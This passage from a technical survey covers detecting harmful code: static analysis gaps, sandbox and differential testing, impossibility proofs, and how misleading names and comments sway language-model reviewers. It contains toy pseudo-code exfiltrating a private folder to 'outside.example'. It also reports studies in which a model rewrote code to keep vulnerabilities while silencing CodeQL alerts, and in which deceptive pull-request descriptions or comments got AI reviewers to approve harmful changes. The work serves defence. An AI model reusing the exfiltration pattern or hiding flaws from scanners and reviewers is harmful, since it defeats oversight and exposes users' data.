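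The change on PrimeVul is one extra vulnerable function caught out of 40. On SVEN, the model stopped catching about a quarter of the vulnerabilities once the names were removed. SVEN is the only one of the three sets not used in training, so it is the best guide to how the model would do on unfamiliar code.

The likely reason is that a slice still contains the names the programmer chose. Slicing removes comments, which is why deleting them made no difference to the results, but it keeps names such as `stolen` and `summary`. Replacing these names with placeholders in every slice before the model reads it would ensure that they can't affect the verdict. This might reduce accuracy. Grasso and colleagues' models lost three or four percentage points, but their inputs had library names removed as well.

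Lekssays and colleagues also altered the slices rather than the original programs, so their test doesn't show whether renaming would mislead the model that writes the queries. Altering the slices may have made the test too harsh, too. Adding code that never runs raised the miss rate on PrimeVul from 55% to 67.5%, but a slicer run on the altered program might have removed some of that code before the model read it.

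More text can mislead a model even when the names stay the same. *Representation Matters* (2026) describes a test on a repaired function from FreeRDP, a remote-desktop program. Given only graphs of the code, a language model correctly classified the function as safe in all six trials. In all three trials that added the source text, it classified the function as vulnerable because it focused on an unrelated calculation. This is a single case, but it supports giving a model less to read.

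Other systems let the language model decide what to extract. In *Bridging Code Property Graphs and Language Models for Program Analysis* (2026), the model can request a slice or trace a piece of data whenever it needs to. In one trial, the model used these tools to correctly fix a flaw in the widely used library libxml2 on its first attempt.

### Where the visible code ends

All of these systems depend on the path being found in the first place. That becomes harder when the data passes through a library function on its way:

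```
summary = read_all(folder)
packed = compress(summary)
send(packed, "outside.example")
```

The analyser may not have the code of `compress`, or may take too long to analyse it. It then relies on a *library model*, a hand-written summary of how the function passes data on. For `compress`, the summary would record that the output is the input in compressed form. The analyser needs this model to follow the path through to `send`. Otherwise it stops at `compress` and reports nothing, even though the program sends the files.

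An analyser could treat every unknown function as passing on everything it receives. This would catch the paths that run through those functions, but it would also mark a lot of harmless data as sensitive and raise the false-alarm rate. Most designers accept some missed paths instead. A library model can also be incomplete. It might cover only some of the results a function returns, or only one of the ways programmers call the function.

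### Alerts that vanish while the flaw remains

*Preserve the Vulnerability, Break the Alert* (Cao, Ding and Xu, 2026) measures how much these gaps matter in CodeQL, the analyser behind GitHub's code scanning service. Projects often run CodeQL on every proposed change. If an alert disappears after a change, people tend to assume that the change fixed the problem.

The researchers began with known vulnerabilities in npm packages where people had already marked the source and the sink. CodeQL correctly reported 172 of these flows. An outsider could use 105 of them to reach off-limits files, 60 to run commands, and seven to insert code into a web page. Claude Opus 4.7, a language model, then rewrote one function along each flow, three separate times. It received CodeQL's alert but no information about how CodeQL works. The researchers instructed it to keep the flaw but stop CodeQL from reporting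 it, and to make the change look like routine maintenance.

Of 514 valid rewrites, 70 removed the CodeQL alert but left the flaw in place. On average, CodeQL stopped reporting 13.6% of the flows after one attempt, 21.1% after two and 26.2% after three. The run cost about $23. One researcher checked every rewrite by hand, and a second checked all 70 successes and a tenth of the others. They traced the data from source to sink but didn't attack the rewritten programs to confirm that the flaws could still be exploited.

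The same model also refactored the same functions without being given the alert or told about any flaw. It produced 516 rewrites, and CodeQL reported the original flow in every one. The median rewrite changed 14 lines, compared with three for the rewrites that silenced an alert, and many added named variables. Cao and colleagues did not test renaming separately, but when the model had the alert and only passed the data through extra variables, it failed to silence the alert in all 45 attempts. CodeQL appears to cope very well with the kind of rewording that defeats a keyword filter.

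CodeQL's failures came mostly from gaps in its library models. Of the 70 successful rewrites, 64 sent the data through a library function that CodeQL already had a model for, but in a way the model didn't cover. Three used a function with no model, and the other three exposed weaknesses in how CodeQL follows data through ordinary code. A single omission accounted for 43 of the 70. In each case, the alert came back when the researchers restored only the operation they suspected and left the rest of the rewrite in place, which is good evidence that they had found the cause. The results also fit the condition in the completeness proof by Dalla Preda and colleagues, since the tracking was mostly sound but the information supplied to it was not.

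This can happen without anyone intending harm. GitHub's automatic repair tool, Copilot Autofix, suggests changes in response to CodeQL alerts, and GitHub counts a suggestion as successful if the alert disappears, no new one appears and the program still passes its tests. Those tests usually check that the program works, not that the flaw is gone. A programmer who keeps editing until the alert clears can also leave the flaw in place. The 26.2% figure doesn't measure how often this happens, because the model in the experiment was told to preserve the flaw, whereas a repair tool tries to remove it.

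Using several analysers together helped less than one might expect. Cao and colleagues ran the same rewrites through ODGen, which traces data with a different design, and njsscan, which matches patterns in the code. Thirty of the 70 successful rewrites came from flows that both tools had detected in the original programs. All three analysers missed 16 of these 30 (53%). With so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be from 36% to 70%. Nearly all the evidence concerns file access.

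ODGen missed 74% of the rewrites that silenced CodeQL and that it could be tested on, but only 24% of the rewrites that CodeQL caught. The two designs therefore share a weakness, though for different internal reasons. For njsscan, the figures were 58% and 48%, close enough that its misses probably have more to do with rewriting in general than with this shared weakness.

The study covers only JavaScript, and the researchers themselves judged whether each change looked natural. It also starts from flaws that CodeQL can find. Earlier research cited by Cao and colleagues found that the three best tools together detected only 57.6% of the vulnerabilities in the full collection, so an analyser's overall miss rate can be far higher than the share of detections it loses when code is rewritten.

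The gaps can be repaired, but all 70 rewrites still worked against a newer release of CodeQL. Its developers could extend the library models and routinely rerun the $23 experiment to test new versions. They would have to watch the false-alarm rate, because some of the omissions may be deliberate. For someone reviewing a single change, Cao and colleagues recommend asking for more than a clean scan, such as a manual trace of the data or a test that tries to exploit the original flaw.

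## Running the software and recording its effects

A data-flow analyser with no library model for `compress` loses track of the files there. If a reviewer runs the program instead, the real `compress` packs the files and the real `send` tries to send them. A *sandbox run* executes the program in an isolated environment that records its effects, and the reviewer judges the program by that record. Renaming the program's variables doesn't change those effects. But the reviewer has to get the program to misbehave during the run, which can be difficult.

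### One run from start to finish

The reviewer first isolates the program so that it can't damage a real machine or reach real data. In *Preflight*, Jandali, Sheybani and colleagues (2026) check Python packages by running each one with limited resources and no administrator rights in a Docker container, a sealed-off environment with its own file system. When the package looks up an internet address, a fake name server inside the sandbox logs the request and answers it, so the package reaches nobody outside.

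The program also needs something to act on. A program that steals files, for example, can't do so on an empty machine. *Runtime Skill Audit* (2026) describes how to prepare a sandbox for *agent skills*, which are packages of written instructions, often with scripts, that an AI agent loads to perform a task. Before each run, the system creates the files, folders and mock credentials that the task requires. It also provides mock versions of services the sandbox lacks, such as a Gmail command, because a skill that can't find its mail account may stop before it does anything worth recording.

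A decoy folder with a diary, a bank statement and a step-count log would be enough for the four programs in the grid. Each file contains a marker, such as "heron-4471", that appears nowhere else. If a marker turns up in outgoing traffic, the reviewer knows which file it came from.

The reviewer then runs the program and records what happens. On Linux, a tool called strace logs *system calls*, the requests a program makes to the operating system to open a file, start another program or connect to a network. Jandali and colleagues also capture network traffic and compare the file system before and after the run. The Open Source Security Foundation, an industry body, runs a similar system for whole package libraries. According to the project's own description, *Package Analysis*, the system watches for new packages and passes each one to a pool of workers that run it in a sandbox. It checks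 which files a package accesses, which addresses it connects to and which commands it runs (Brown and Wheeler, 2022, *Introducing Package Analysis*). In its first month, the system identified more than 200 malicious packages on PyPI and npm.

The raw log is full of temporary file names and process numbers, so the reviewer reduces it to a short list of named behaviours. For the grid, the result might be:

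| Program | Reads | Sends | Prints | Named behaviour |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `steal_private_files` (harmful) | all decoy files | all three markers, to outside.example | nothing | private files leave the machine |
| `build_wellness_report` (harmful) | all decoy files | all three markers, to outside.example | nothing | private files leave the machine |
| `steal_passwords` (harmless) | nothing | nothing | "test passed" | none |
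| `build_wellness_report` (honest) | step-count log | nothing | step count | none |

In a sandbox, the reviewer can also test for consent by acting as the user. If a program asks for permission, the reviewer can run it twice, answering "yes" once and "no" once. If the program sends files out after a "no", it does so without the user's consent. If the program never asks, the reviewer still has to find out whether the user agreed in some other way.

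The last step is to classify the package. Jandali and colleagues use a fixed rule: two or more critical findings make a package malicious, one makes it suspicious, and none makes it clean, unless a static scan finds something critical. The findings counted under such a rule need to be checked. The system correctly classified a compromised release of DurableTask as malicious, but it did so because of three network addresses, two of which belonged to the sandbox itself. Without those two, it would have classified the release as suspicious.

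People can also review the flags. In *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026) searched 17,022 skills from a public marketplace for ones that expose passwords or access keys. They used keyword matching and code analysis to narrow these to 3,156, ran those in a sandbox with mock credentials, and flagged 1,427. Three reviewers then confirmed 520, about 36% of the flagged skills. The researchers never ran the 8,343 skills that contained none of the keywords, so nobody knows how many of those leak credentials.

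### Comparing two versions

Many harmless packages connect to the internet, write files and start other programs. *Differential testing* helps separate these from suspicious ones. The reviewer gives the same inputs to two versions of a program and compares the effects.

Jandali and colleagues do this with successive releases of a package. Let F(P, A) be the set of named behaviours that package P shows when the sandbox uses it the way application A does. The behaviours that are new in the later release are

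New = F(P_later, A) \ F(P_earlier, A),

where the backslash means "in the first set but not in the second". For Ultralytics, a computer-vision package that attackers compromised in 2024, the difference between versions 8.3.40 and 8.3.41 included a new network address and a new outside program. Neither would mean much alone, but a minor update to an image-recognition tool has little reason to introduce both.

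An empty difference means only that the observed behaviour didn't change. Comparing `steal_private_files` with the harmful `build_wellness_report` would show no difference, though both do harm. If an earlier release already contacted a server for good reasons, a later one could start sending private data to the same server without adding anything to the list of addresses.

Auditors can also compare runs in different environments. *SkillSentry* (2026) describes running an agent skill in an ordinary environment and in a matching one with a tempting decoy irrelevant to the task. Another run without the skill shows what the agent would have done anyway. The system judges the state of the environment before and after, because the agent's account of its actions may be wrong.

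When the wellness program compresses the files, it scrambles the markers, so a search of the outgoing traffic may find nothing. The reviewer can instead run the program twice, changing only the diary. If the outgoing data differs between the two runs but stays the same when the reviewer repeats a run unchanged, the program is sending information about the diary off the machine.

### Searching for inputs that break a rule

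Differential testing needs a second version or a second environment. *Property-based testing* needs a rule that should hold for every input. For the wellness program, the rule might be:

*For every folder and every answer from the user, if the user has not agreed, no private file leaves the machine.*

A testing tool generates many folders and answers, runs the program on each, and checks after every run whether the program broke the rule. Suppose the program sends the folder only if it holds more than 50 files. A decoy folder with three files would never expose this, but a tool that tries folders of every size up to 100 would soon catch it breaking the rule. Many such tools then simplify the failing input as far as they can. Here they would reduce it to a folder of 51 files, which would help the reviewer see what makes the program send a folder.

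*Fuzz testing* is a related method that is crude but very successful. It feeds a program random input and usually counts any crash or hang as a failure. Shafique, Miller and Heymann (2026), in *A Study of the Reliability of Agentic AI-Generated Programs*, used it to compare software written by people with software written by AI agents. Agents running Claude Opus 4.8, a language model from Anthropic, wrote new versions of ten standard Linux utilities from their documentation. The researchers tested both versions of each utility with the same 4,280 random test cases, about 12 gigabytes of data, and with AFL++, a tool that detects when an input reaches new code and then tries variations of it. They ran riskier programs in containers, because random text typed into a command shell is occasionally a real command, such as one to reboot.

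The tests exposed 24 distinct failures, 19 in the human-written versions and five in the AI-written ones. Some of the difference arose because AI-written programs did less, and even a program that did nothing would pass this kind of test. The AI-written shell avoided one crash because it rejects an unusual construction that the original tries to process. The AI-written file-transfer program avoided another because it silently discards accented letters and other non-English characters typed at its prompt.

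A clean record is weak evidence that a program is harmless unless the reviewer also confirms that the program did its ordinary work during the run. A program that crashes on startup, for example, sends no private files.

### What a clean run leaves open

A run shows only what happened on the paths the program took, and there may be a great many others. A program with 30 independent yes-or-no decisions has 2^30 possible paths, more than a billion.

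If a behaviour appears on a fraction p of inputs, the chance that n independent random tests all miss it is

(1 − p)^n.

If a behaviour appears on one input in 10,000, a thousand tests will miss it about 90% of the time (0.9999^1000 ≈ 0.905). Ten thousand tests will still miss it 37% of the time, and reducing the miss rate to 5% takes about 30,000 tests.

The calculation also gives an upper limit on how common an undetected behaviour is likely to be. If n tests all come out clean, a behaviour that appears on more than about 3/n of inputs is unlikely, because the tests would have detected it at least 95% of the time. A thousand clean runs make a frequency above about 0.3% unlikely but don't rule out anything rarer. The same limit applies to measurements of the sandbox itself. Jandali and colleagues ran 100 harmless packages without a false alarm, which is encouraging but compatible with a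 false-alarm rate of up to about 3%.

These figures assume that the tests draw inputs from the same range as real use. Malicious software often breaks that assumption. *CHASE* (Toda and Mori, 2026) describes a PyPI package, ethereim, that checked during installation whether it was on a Windows computer. If it was, the package decrypted hidden code that downloaded more code from a website and ran it. Repeated runs in a Linux sandbox would never have revealed this behavior. One remedy is to run packages on several operating systems. Another, described in *PyFEX* (2026), is to force the program down both branches of such a check. This improves detection of packages that examine their surroundings, but it can also expose paths that no real run would take.

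The result also depends on which part of a package the reviewer runs. Toda and Mori cite earlier research which found that 87.6% of malicious packages act as soon as someone installs or imports them, so the rest need a further trigger. Jandali and colleagues tested two compromised packages, Ultralytics and ctx. Both appeared clean when the sandbox only imported them, but malicious when it called the functions that a real application would use. A language model wrote the short programs that make these calls, and nine of them cost about three cents in total.

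Their results for LiteLLM, a library for connecting applications to language models, show that a verdict can depend on how an application uses a package. The sandbox compared versions 1.82.6 and 1.82.7 twice. The first application only sent requests to a model, and the sandbox found nothing new and returned "clean". It returned "malicious" after finding 14 critical behaviours when a second application started LiteLLM's proxy server, which contained the compromised code. The researchers added the second application as an exploratory test, so the result doesn't show that the system would have found the problem without guidance. They treat both verdicts as correct, since each concerns one application's use of the package. The clean verdict would no longer be useful once the first application started using the proxy server, so Jandali and colleagues tie each verdict to an exact copy of the application.

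Even good search methods miss some crashes. The fuzz tests by Shafique and colleagues found 17 distinct crashes, seven with plain random input and ten with AFL++, and none with both. Three of the 17 were in a program that AFL++ couldn't run, but the other 14 show that a second method can find many crashes the first missed.

### The `make` that could hardly build anything

Before the fuzz tests, Shafique and colleagues had to get the AI-written utilities to work. One agent turned the documentation into a checklist of features and a set of tests. Other agents wrote the code, and agents that hadn't seen it being written audited it.

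The utility `make` builds large programs from source code by working out which parts need building and running the right commands. The AI-written version passed all its generated tests and went through more than 20 rounds of audit, but at first it could build little beyond a simple C program. The researchers discovered this when they used it to build real software, including three configurations of the Linux kernel and 17 other packages, such as the databases PostgreSQL and SQLite. The builds exposed several missing or incomplete features, which took about another week to fix.

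The file viewer `less` had a similar problem on a smaller scale. Eleven of its options did nothing because the program accepted and stored them, but no other part of the code used them. They remained after four audit rounds and a set of tests in which 1,217 of 1,221 passed, partly because some tests checked only that the program accepted an option. A simple differential test that ran `less` with and without each option and compared the screen output could have caught many of them.

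A passed test is good evidence of a function only if the test would probably fail without that function. The same kind of agent wrote both the code and the tests for `make`, using the same documentation. Twenty audit rounds then failed to detect that `make` could barely build anything. If each round had independently had a 50% chance of detecting this, the chance of all 20 missing it would have been about one in a million. The rounds probably shared a blind spot, so repeating them helped little. Building the Linux kernel was much stronger evidence, because a program is very unlikely to do that without the necessary features.

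Tests from an outside source help, but they also have gaps. In the search tool `grep`, a missing option went undetected through four audit rounds, the agents' tests and the original project's test suite. Shafique and colleagues suggest a separate review of the tests to distinguish those that check a feature's effect from those that check only whether the program runs.

This study concerns missing functions. Ordinary tests are even weaker evidence when a harm reviewer is looking for functions that shouldn't be there. If the harmful `build_wellness_report` also printed an accurate step count, it could pass every step-count test while sending the folder to an outside address.

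### Why no procedure is always right

Better testing can narrow these gaps, but a proof from the theory of computing shows that nobody can close them for all programs. Suppose someone claims to have a perfect detector. It accepts any program, always finishes, and correctly reports whether the program would ever send private files out. Now take an arbitrary program Q and put it inside another program:

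```
function R():
    run_isolated(Q)
    steal_private_files(folder)
```

`run_isolated` runs Q but throws away anything Q tries to write or send, so Q itself can't do the harm. R therefore steals the files if Q eventually stops, and never reaches the second line if Q runs forever. Anyone who used the detector to check whether R is harmful would also learn whether Q stops.

The mathematician Alan Turing proved in the 1930s that no procedure can answer that question for every program. If one existed, someone could write a program that applies the procedure to itself, then runs forever if the answer is "stops" and stops if the answer is "runs forever". Either answer would be wrong, so the procedure can't exist, and neither can the perfect detector. Evans gives this argument for viruses in *On the Impossibility of Virus Detection* and explains why the isolation is necessary. Without it, Q might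 steal the files and then run forever. The detector would rightly call R harmful, but that would no longer show that Q stops.

Rice (1953), in *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, proved that if some programs have a given property and others lack it, and the property concerns what programs compute, then no general method can decide for every program whether it has that property. The theorem applies to behaviour, not wording. Lexical audits always produce an answer because checking a program's text is easier than determining its behaviour. For example, a keyword filter can check any program for the word "steal" in a single pass.

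Cohen (1984), in *Cure of Computer Viruses*, reached the same conclusion about viruses more directly. He imagined a program that runs a virus detector on itself and infects other programs only if the detector reports that it is not a virus, so whatever the detector reports is wrong. He used a similar construction to show that no procedure can always decide whether two versions of a program are equivalent. Differential testing can therefore prove that two programs differ by finding an input on which they behave differently, but no version of it can always prove that they are equivalent.

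These proofs rule out a method that is right about every program, but not one that is right about nearly all the programs people write. Rice noted that special methods will exist for particular functions, and Cohen noted that a suitable scheme can detect any particular virus. A detector that always finishes must make some mistakes, but its designer can choose between more misses and more false alarms.

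The proofs also assume unlimited memory. A real computer has a finite number of possible states, so in theory a reviewer could run a program until it stopped or repeated a state. Evans points out that this is hopeless in practice. A machine with just 16 kilobytes of memory has 2^131,072 possible states, a number with more than 39,000 digits. (Evans gives 81 digits, which is far too low.)

### What reviewers can still guarantee

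A reviewer can find out whether a program sends private files in its first million steps on a given input, even when the reviewer can't find out whether it will ever send them. If the program has 20 yes-or-no settings and no other input, there are 1,048,576 combinations to test. At one second each, 100 machines could test them all in about three hours. The result is guaranteed for those settings and the first million steps, but the program might still send the files later.

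Another approach is to restrict the language in which people write the programs. Evans notes that a program always finishes if its instructions can never jump backwards, which rules out loops. An auditor can then run the program to the end on any input, but that may not be enough. Rice showed that his result still holds for functions that always give an answer, because there are infinitely many inputs to check. A stronger restriction is to leave out the dangerous operation. If a language has no way to reach a network, no program written in it can send files anywhere. If the only way to reach a network is to write `send`, and programs can't look up functions by name while they run, then a keyword search for `send` finds every program that could do it.

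Reviewers can also leave the program as it is and deny it the permissions it needs to do harm. Without network access, the harmful `build_wellness_report` still reads the folder and calls `send`, but the operating system refuses the connection. Nobody has to predict what the program will do. Evans explains that the impossibility result doesn't apply to changing or confining a program in this way, and that the hard part is blocking harmful actions without blocking useful ones. For example, a backup tool needs both the files and the network. The user can allow it to contact only one chosen server, but that doesn't control what it sends there.

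Chen and colleagues report that many agent skills run directly on the user's computer with all the access of the program that hosts them, including saved credentials and the network. Restricting that access would stop many kinds of theft, but someone has to know which effects to restrict. Of the 1,371 issues they attributed to careless developers, 73.5% involved skills that printed credentials in routine debugging messages. Printing is harmless in most programs, but agent software passes whatever a skill prints to the language model. Anyone who can talk to the model may then be able to get the credential by asking for it, even if the skill has no network access.

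## Language models as code reviewers, and how far names sway them

A reviewer can also ask a language model what the code does. If the model relies on the calls in the harmful `build_wellness_report`, it might answer that the function reads every file in a folder and sends the contents to an outside address. It might instead rely on the names and answer that the function prepares and delivers a wellness report.

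A language model can find a renamed function because renaming removes only some of the evidence of what the function does. The calls to `read_all` and `send`, their order and the variable connecting them remain. The model can recognise these without a list of sources and sinks because it learned to predict the next token in huge amounts of text, including code that reads files and sends data under many different variable names. But most programmers choose names that fit, so names are also good predictors, and training does little to reduce a model's reliance on them. Names can't influence an analyser that has replaced them with placeholders, but researchers have to measure how much they influence a language model.

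### Missing names and misleading names

In a set of experiments called Face/Off, Shen and colleagues measured how far names sway language models. They showed models the same functions with their original names, with placeholders such as `func0` and `var1`, and with misleading names borrowed from an unrelated function.

In one task, the model had to decide whether a description matched a function. GPT-4o-mini accepted 76.5% of the correct descriptions when the functions had their original names, 59.5% when they had placeholders, and 39.2% when they had misleading names. This looks as if the model understood less of the code once the names were gone, but a second task suggests otherwise. The model saw the correct description next to the one for the function that had supplied the misleading names, and had to choose between them:

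| Model | Original names | Anonymous names | Misleading names |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 98.98% | 98.98% | 76.11% |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 | 98.98% | 98.63% | 78.66% |
| Llama 3 70B | 98.63% | 98.63% | 73.27% |
| GPT-3.5-turbo | 92.84% | 81.35% | 52.39% |

GPT-4o-mini chose between descriptions just as well with placeholders as with the original names. In the first task, placeholders had apparently made it less likely to say yes without making it worse at telling which description fitted. Misleading names did more damage: GPT-4o-mini chose the wrong description in nearly a quarter of cases, and GPT-3.5-turbo performed close to chance.

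In one example, GPT-3.5-turbo received the beginning of a function that calculates how far a set of numbers lies from its average. The function's misleading names referred to counting even and odd numbers, and the model completed the function to do that instead.

Face/Off also tested one-sentence summaries, but those results are harder to interpret because the score depends on how many words a summary shares with a reference text. GPT-3.5-turbo's summaries scored 15.04 on functions whose words and symbols had all been shuffled into random order and 14.97 on intact functions with placeholder names, so the model can evidently pick up the right topic from the words alone.

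The researchers also ran a control in which the name shouldn't matter. They chose 317 variables whose type (number, list, text and so on) was clear from the surrounding code, and asked three models to identify the type. GPT-4o-mini was right 82.6% of the time with the original name, 79.5% with a placeholder and 84.9% with a misleading name. For all three models, the differences from the original name were small enough to be due to chance. Names therefore seem to matter less when nearby code makes the answer clear, but the control was also a milder test because it changed only one name.

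All the models in Face/Off are old. The four in the table date from 2024 or earlier and are much weaker than the models reviewers can use now.

### A correct description beside a wrong name

In a more recent case study, *Poisoned Identifiers Survive LLM Deobfuscation*, Guzmán Lorenzo (2026) asked Claude Opus 4.6, an Anthropic model from early 2026, to make JavaScript programs readable again after a tool had scrambled them. The names in the programs were wrong before the scrambling. In a physics simulation, for example, the force that pushes points apart was named `attraction`.

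Claude corrected wrong names when it was given readable code. When the code had been scrambled, Claude kept at least some of the wrong names in all eight standard runs on the simulation and in all five on a route-finding program. Guzmán Lorenzo then tried four prompts, three times each. Three of them included an instruction to check the names, and one of those also included a warning that someone might have chosen the names to mislead. Claude kept wrong names in all 12 runs.

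In 15 of 17 runs on the simulation, the model kept the wrong name in the code even though it described the operation correctly in a comment or explanation. Guzmán Lorenzo judged the runs alone and knew which names were wrong, so the exact count is uncertain.

Changing the task worked better than telling the model to be careful. When the prompt asked for an implementation from scratch, the model kept the name `attraction` in one of five runs. On the route-finding program, it kept none of the wrong names in five runs. Checks confirmed that the new versions still had the main parts of each algorithm.

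In what seems to be a single exploratory run, Claude also replaced names that sounded like malware with suitable ones it worked out from the algorithm. This would be useful if the result holds up, because alarming names on harmless code cause many of a keyword filter's false alarms. One possible explanation is that Claude may detect a consistent vocabulary that doesn't fit the code. In replicated tests, it corrected the names in all five runs when every name came from engineering, but kept unrelated words such as `combustion` in all five when the names came from no particular field.

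The case study shows that a reviewer should read what the model writes about the operations and not rely on the names in its cleaned-up code. A fresh copy of Claude, asked to check those names, noticed problems but didn't fully correct them in any of three runs. The study covers two harmless programs of roughly 110 to 130 lines, so it doesn't show whether bland names would hide a harmful function from the same model.

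### People reading the same code

Misleading names can fool people too. *Do Machines Struggle Where Humans Do?* (Le, Nguyen and Nguyen, 2026) compared seven models with 50 computer science undergraduates from an earlier experiment. Each model and student had to predict the exact output of a function of fewer than 15 lines for a given input.

The best model, a small version of DeepSeek-R1, was right 63.8% of the time with the original names, 64.2% with uninformative names and 51.8% with misleading ones. The second-best, SmolLM3-3B, scored 45.0%, 44.0% and 34.2% in the same conditions. In Face/Off, too, removing names mattered much less than replacing them with false ones. The other five models were right less than a quarter of the time in every condition, too rarely to tell much about the effect of names.

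The students' average fell only slightly, from 40.5% with the original names to 38.0% with misleading ones. The most experienced students improved from 40.5% to 55.6%, which no model matched. Le and colleagues take this as a sign that experienced programmers rely more on structure. But these percentages represent about 17 correct answers out of 42 and 15 out of 27, so the improvement could easily be chance.

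The models were also small, with at most eight billion parameters (the adjustable numbers inside a model), so the study provides little evidence about the large models that companies use for code review. On a separate set of 50 tasks in the same study, misleading names raised the models' confidence in their wrong answers on 24 tasks and lowered it on 26, compared with uninformative names. A reviewer therefore can't rely on low confidence to show that names have misled a model.

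### Comments and descriptions

A program's author also controls its comments and accompanying description. Studies differ on how much false reassurance in this text affects a model's review.

Thornton (2026), in *LLM Code Reviewers Are Harder to Fool Than You Think*, found that comments had almost no effect on whether models detected vulnerabilities. Thornton wrote 100 programs with one vulnerability each and had eight models review versions with the same code but different comments, for 9,366 trials in total. Claude Opus 4.6 detected 95% of the vulnerabilities without comments and 94% with comments falsely claiming that the code was safe. GPT-5.2 went from 93% to 92%, and DeepSeek Chat rose from 89% to 93%. None of the eight models' detection rates changed by a statistically significant amount.

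The comments could still have a small effect. With 100 programs, Thornton's test would reliably detect ten extra misses, but five would fall just short of the usual standard of significance. The scoring may also have hidden some misses. A response counted as a detection if it contained a listed keyword for the vulnerability, so a model that repeated a comment's false denial would get credit for finding the flaw. A hand check of 14 responses to the most elaborate comments found one such error. Thornton argues that scoring errors cancel out because the same keywords apply to both versions of a program, but this error can occur only in the version with comments.

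Mitropoulos, Alexopoulos and colleagues (2026), in *Measuring and Exploiting Confirmation Bias in LLM-Assisted Security Code Review*, found much larger effects. They gave four older models 247 vulnerable files from real projects and 250 repaired ones. In one condition they used a neutral prompt, and in another they told the models that the file was free of a particular type of flaw. They also checked by hand whether each flag on a vulnerable file identified the real flaw.

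| Model | Vulnerable files flagged, neutral → "bug-free" | Repaired files flagged, neutral | Real flaws found, neutral → "bug-free" |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o-mini | 97.2% → 3.6% | 96.8% | 31.2% → 3.2% |
| Claude 3.5 Haiku | 68.4% → 8.5% | 68.4% | 19.8% → 5.3% |
| DeepSeek V3 | 96.8% → 53.8% | 95.2% | 32.8% → 29.1% |
| Gemini 2.0 Flash | 95.5% → 79.4% | 92.8% | 40.5% → 36.8% |

GPT-4o-mini's drop from 97.2% to 3.6% is less informative than it looks, because the model had also been flagging 96.8% of the repaired files. DeepSeek V3 flagged far fewer vulnerable files after the false claim but found nearly as many real flaws as before. GPT-4o-mini and Claude 3.5 Haiku lost most of their real detections.

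Moon, Hwang and colleagues (2026), in *Don't Judge Code by Its Cover*, saw a similar shift when they asked models whether programs were correct. Comments that misdescribed the task lowered GPT-4o's accuracy on correct Java programs from 86.5% to 59.8%, but raised its accuracy on incorrect ones from 63.3% to 78.5%. Its balanced accuracy fell only from 74.9% to 69.2%, because the comments mainly made the model more likely to call any program incorrect. A reviewer can partly offset this shift by changing the threshold for flagging a program, but that won't help if the model can no longer tell good code from bad.

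Mitropoulos and colleagues also tested complete review tools. They prepared *pull requests*, which are proposed changes to a project's code, with a title and description. Each one undid an earlier security repair, but its description presented the change as safe or as an improvement. GitHub Copilot, which answers questions from a human reviewer, approved six of 34 and gave an unclear verdict on another six. Claude Code, set up as an automatic reviewer with the instructions that real projects use, failed to reject 13 of 17 on the first attempt. The researchers could revise each description up to three times after seeing the review, and Claude Code eventually approved 16 of the 17.

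Deleting the descriptions or telling the tools to ignore them reversed most of these results. When the researchers told Copilot to look only at the code, it rejected all 12 of the changes it had missed. Claude Code rejected 11 of the 16 it had missed once they deleted the description, and four more when they also told it to ignore the remaining notes. In two of the five cases where deletion wasn't enough, Claude Code's review had praised a comment in the code itself.

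The researchers retested only the failures, and a model may answer differently on a second try by chance. Chance is unlikely to explain the Copilot result, though. Copilot rejected about 65% of the changes the first time, and at that rate it would reject 12 in a row less than 1% of the time.

Some script authors have already tried to influence AI reviewers. Cloudflare's *Threat report* (2026) describes scripts containing text intended to manipulate the internet infrastructure company's detection systems, which it found on its own platform in March 2026. Its researchers then tested seven models on 100 malicious or abusive scripts. According to SecurityBrief Asia's *Cloudflare warns of AI code review prompt injection* (2026), the average detection rate fell from 67.3% to 53.3% when misleading comments made up less than 1% of a file. When they made up more than 25%, the rate rose to 97.9%, possibly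 because so much repeated reassurance looks suspicious.

File size had a larger effect. The models detected nearly all malicious scripts under 500 kilobytes, but only 12% to 18% of those over three megabytes, where the harmful part was buried in ordinary library code. File size also makes the comment figures harder to interpret, because the same number of comments takes up a smaller share of a large file. The "less than 1%" group may therefore have contained more large files, which the models tend to miss anyway, and the "more than 25%" group may have contained more small ones.

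### Why the results differ

| Study | Where the false reassurance was | Code under review | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Thornton | comments | 15 to 60 lines | no significant change |
| Mitropoulos and colleagues, older models | the reviewer's prompt | median of 707 lines | real flaws found fell by 4 to 28 percentage points |
| Mitropoulos and colleagues, review tools | descriptions, notes and some comments | changes to real code | 12 of 34 and 16 of 17 harmful changes not rejected |
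| Cloudflare | comments | up to several megabytes | detection fell by 14 percentage points |

The age and strength of the models can't fully explain the conflict. Three of Thornton's models were small enough to run locally and found only 53% to 72% of the flaws, yet comments didn't sway them significantly either. Claude Code used much newer models than those in the first experiment by Mitropoulos and colleagues, but it still approved nearly all the harmful changes. Strength may matter within a single study. In Cloudflare's tests, the detection rate of one of the cheaper models fell from 90% to 67% after the researchers added 20 comments, while small numbers of comments had little effect on several of the most advanced models.

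The difficulty of finding the flaw probably matters more. The commercial models Thornton tested found 89% to 96% of the flaws without help, so the code usually gave them clear evidence. In the files that Mitropoulos and colleagues used, the repair usually changed no more than five lines out of several hundred. A model that can't find clear evidence in the code may rely more on what someone tells it. The type-inference control in Face/Off fits this explanation, since names had little effect when nearby code determined the answer.

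The position of the text may matter too. In the first experiment by Mitropoulos and colleagues, the false claim was in the prompt, which models are trained to follow. A comment is part of the material under review, so a model has more reason to doubt it. The purpose of the text also differed, since the descriptions for Claude Code were written to argue for one particular change and could be improved after each review, while Thornton's comments were fixed in advance.

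None of these studies varied difficulty, position and effort separately, so we can't tell how much each contributes. The safest reading is that a false comment in a short program probably won't mislead a good model, but that reviewers shouldn't rely on this in a long file or a subtle change.

### Reviewing code without its names

One response is a *name-blind review*, in which the model has to describe what the code does before it sees the author's wording. It has four steps:

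1. Save the original, then remove the comments, the description and any other notes. Leave blank lines where the comments were, so that the line numbers stay the same.
2. Use a program to replace every name that the code defines with a short placeholder, and keep a list of the replacements. Don't change library functions, fixed text such as "outside.example", or names that the program looks up while it runs.
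3. Ask the model to list everything the code reads, changes, sends or runs, with line numbers for each effect. Check that those lines really contain the operations.
4. Restore the names and comments, and ask whether they account for every effect on the list. Give a person any effect that they don't account for.

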